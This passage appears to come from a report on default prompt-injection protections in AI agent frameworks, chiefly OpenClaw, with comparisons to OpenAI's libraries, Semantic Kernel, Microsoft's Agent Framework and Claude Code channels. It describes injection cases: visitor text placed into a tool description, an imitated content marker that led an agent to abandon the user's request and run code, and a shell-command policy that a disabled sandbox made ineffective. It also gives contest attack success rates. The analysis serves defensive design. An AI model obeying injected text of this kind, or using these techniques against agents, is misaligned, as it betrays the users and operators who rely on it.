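A safer default can break installations that depended on the old one. When OpenClaw began to require permanent Telegram IDs, many users still had usernames on their approved lists. Without a migration, those contacts would have lost access, and users might not have known why.

The developers therefore added a repair to `openclaw doctor --fix`, a command that corrects configuration problems. The repair looks up the numeric Telegram ID for each username and replaces the name with the number. The lookup returns the account that holds the username when the command runs. If a friend gave up the name and a stranger claimed it, the stranger would get permanent access, so users should check the new list.

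Most of the related fixes mainly removed code. Suwansathit and colleagues take this as evidence that the safe version was available from the start and that developers chose convenience instead.

OpenClaw also keeps older interfaces to support plugins already published. Its developers will review one group of these no earlier than 1 October 2026, and they will not remove an interface until they can show that no published plugin uses it. That group includes a function for adapters that assemble part of the reply process themselves, so the shared path can't be the only one until every plugin that uses the function has changed.

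### What other frameworks do by default

The table compares what developers get without adding protection of their own.

| Product | Where outside text goes | Record of its origin | What the developer must do |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's JavaScript libraries | wherever the developer puts it | the message's role | keep it out of system prompts and tool descriptions |
| Semantic Kernel | the message the developer chose, encoded | none from the encoding | choose the right message, and encode records by hand |
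| Microsoft Agent Framework | depends on the application | trust and secrecy labels, with an experimental feature | adopt the feature and set policies |
| Claude Code channels | the user's Claude Code session | depends on the channel | check who sent each message |
| OpenClaw | a labelled block, on the paths it covers | an optional field | use the shared functions |

OpenAI's libraries accept any string as a system message or a tool description. In an example from GitHub, a program lets a visitor choose a topic and adds it to the description of a search tool, so the visitor can write instructions that the model receives as part of the tool's definition. In GitHub's repaired version, the description contains a fixed list of topics and the tool accepts no other topics. The library accepts both versions without a warning.

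Microsoft's newer Agent Framework includes FIDES and its trust labels. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) says most agents in use rely instead on a defensive system prompt or a homemade list of permitted actions, and that both can fail silently. But according to Microsoft, FIDES is still an experimental feature in a separate module, so it doesn't protect agents built by developers who don't know about it.

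A Claude Code channel connects the coding agent to a chat service such as Telegram or Discord. Each channel is an MCP server, and Anthropic tells channel developers to add sender checks to protect against prompt injection. MCP carries the messages, but each developer decides which senders to trust. OpenClaw also left this decision to each adapter's developer, which led to the same mistake in many places.

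### Plugins that write to the system prompt

A plugin can get around a safe default if the framework gives it direct access to the prompt. OpenClaw's *Prompt and session hooks* describes how plugins can add text before or after the system prompt, or replace it entirely. According to *plugins: enforce prompt hook policy with runtime validation*, a change to OpenClaw's code, the developers let plugins put fixed guidance in the system prompt partly because providers charge less for text that stays the same from one call to the next.

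Fixed guidance from a plugin that the user chose to install may well belong in that position, but the same feature also accepts text that the plugin has just downloaded. OpenClaw limits each plugin's additions to a quarter of the model's context window, but this doesn't restrict whose text a plugin can add.

Plugins can also queue text for the next turn, which OpenClaw adds to the next user message. Another feature lets a plugin search the agent's memory and add what it finds to the context. The documentation's example returns the memories without labelling them, so a developer who copies it might give the model a stranger's words that the agent saved weeks earlier.

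OpenClaw passes plugins the record of origin it added after the flaw in messages between sessions. But the field is optional, and OpenClaw leaves it out of some ordinary messages from people. The documentation warns that "Absence does not prove human origin." A plugin that assumed a message without the field came from the user would repeat the scheduled-job mistake. Treating such messages as untrusted would be safer, but the plugin would sometimes distrust the user.

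### Names for unsafe options

Plugins can change prompts unless the operator sets `allowPromptInjection` to false. Most operators will never type its name, and a conspicuous name works as a warning only if someone has to write it to get the unsafe behaviour. OpenClaw's `allowUnsafeExternalContent` meets that condition, because the wrapper around external content from webhooks and Gmail stays on until an operator sets the option to true.

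OpenClaw's *Security* lists every setting whose name begins with "dangerous" or "dangerously" and gives a command that audits an installation for risky settings. These names also affect who is responsible when something goes wrong, because OpenClaw rejects vulnerability reports whose only complaint is that such an option weakens the defaults. It considers these options "explicit break-glass tradeoffs by design".

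A default setting can sound safe but have no effect. In February 2026, OpenClaw's default policy for shell commands was `deny`. Commands were also set to run in a sandbox by default, and OpenClaw skipped the policy for those commands because the sandbox was supposed to contain any damage. But the sandbox was off by default, and Mint Security found that commands therefore ran directly on the user's machine with no check. Each setting made sense alone, and a reviewer who looked only at the policy would have thought the agent blocked shell commands.

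OpenClaw now refuses to run a command if the operator has explicitly asked for a sandbox and none is available. Commands still run without approval by default, but OpenClaw now discloses this, so its documentation matches the program's behavior.

### How much markers change a model's behaviour

A marker is only text in the model's context, so an attacker can imitate it and the model can ignore it. OpenClaw removes exact copies of its markers from outside text, but a model may accept a similar one. McCauley and colleagues used an imitation to make an OpenClaw agent abandon the user's request and run code, but they did not report how often this worked.

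The OpenClaw derivative openskynet gives each wrapper a random ID so that an attacker can't predict the real marker. Ordinary code could check that ID exactly, but a model might not compare the IDs at all.

OpenClaw's documentation cites a public contest with 272,000 attacks in 41 agent scenarios. An attack counted only if the agent carried out the harmful action and hid it from the user.

| Model | Successful attacks |
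|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 0.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 1.0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 1.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 8.5% |

Attacks succeeded 17 times as often against Gemini 2.5 Pro as against Opus 4.5, so the choice of model matters. But the contest did not compare the same model with and without OpenClaw's markers. The rates would also be higher if they included harmful actions that the agent did not hide. According to OpenClaw, attacks adapted to a particular defence have succeeded more than 80% of the time in published tests.

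Imperva's experiment doesn't measure the markers either, because OpenClaw had put neither the image nor the contact's name inside them.

To find out whether a label helps, researchers would need to send the same attacks to the same model with and without it. A few demonstrations can show only that the label sometimes fails. The test would also have to be large, because attacks on good models rarely succeed. If a label halved the success rate from 1% to 0.5%, researchers would need about 4,700 attacks in each condition to have an 80% chance of detecting the difference at the usual 5% significance level. If the rate started at 8.5%, about 510 attacks in each condition would be enough to detect a halving.

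The results of Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell suggest that labels alone have only a modest effect on the model. But the program can also check a label before it saves text to memory or runs a tool, and that check works whether or not the label affects the model.

### Who bears the cost

Microsoft describes agent security as a shared responsibility. Its framework supplies the components, while application developers must validate inputs, secure data flows and configure tools. Leaving decisions to developers is reasonable when they depend on the application, such as who may approve a payment. It works poorly for tasks that are the same in every application, like labelling a search result, because thousands of developers have to remember them and some will forget.

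Moving that work into the framework means a few developers do it once, but they also get the complaints when an update breaks existing programs. Semantic Kernel's new error stopped code that had previously run, so each affected team had to change its templates. Teams that had been inserting unencoded customer names learned of the mistake, but teams whose data had always been safe had to make the same changes.

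Safe defaults can also cause problems for users. Warnings take up space in the context and add to the cost of each call, and an overcautious label may lead the model to ignore a useful instruction. If a default causes too much trouble, people will switch it off. Semantic Kernel lets developers turn off protection for a single variable or for every template. The single-variable option is safer because a developer who has trouble with one field can exempt it and leave the protection on for the rest.
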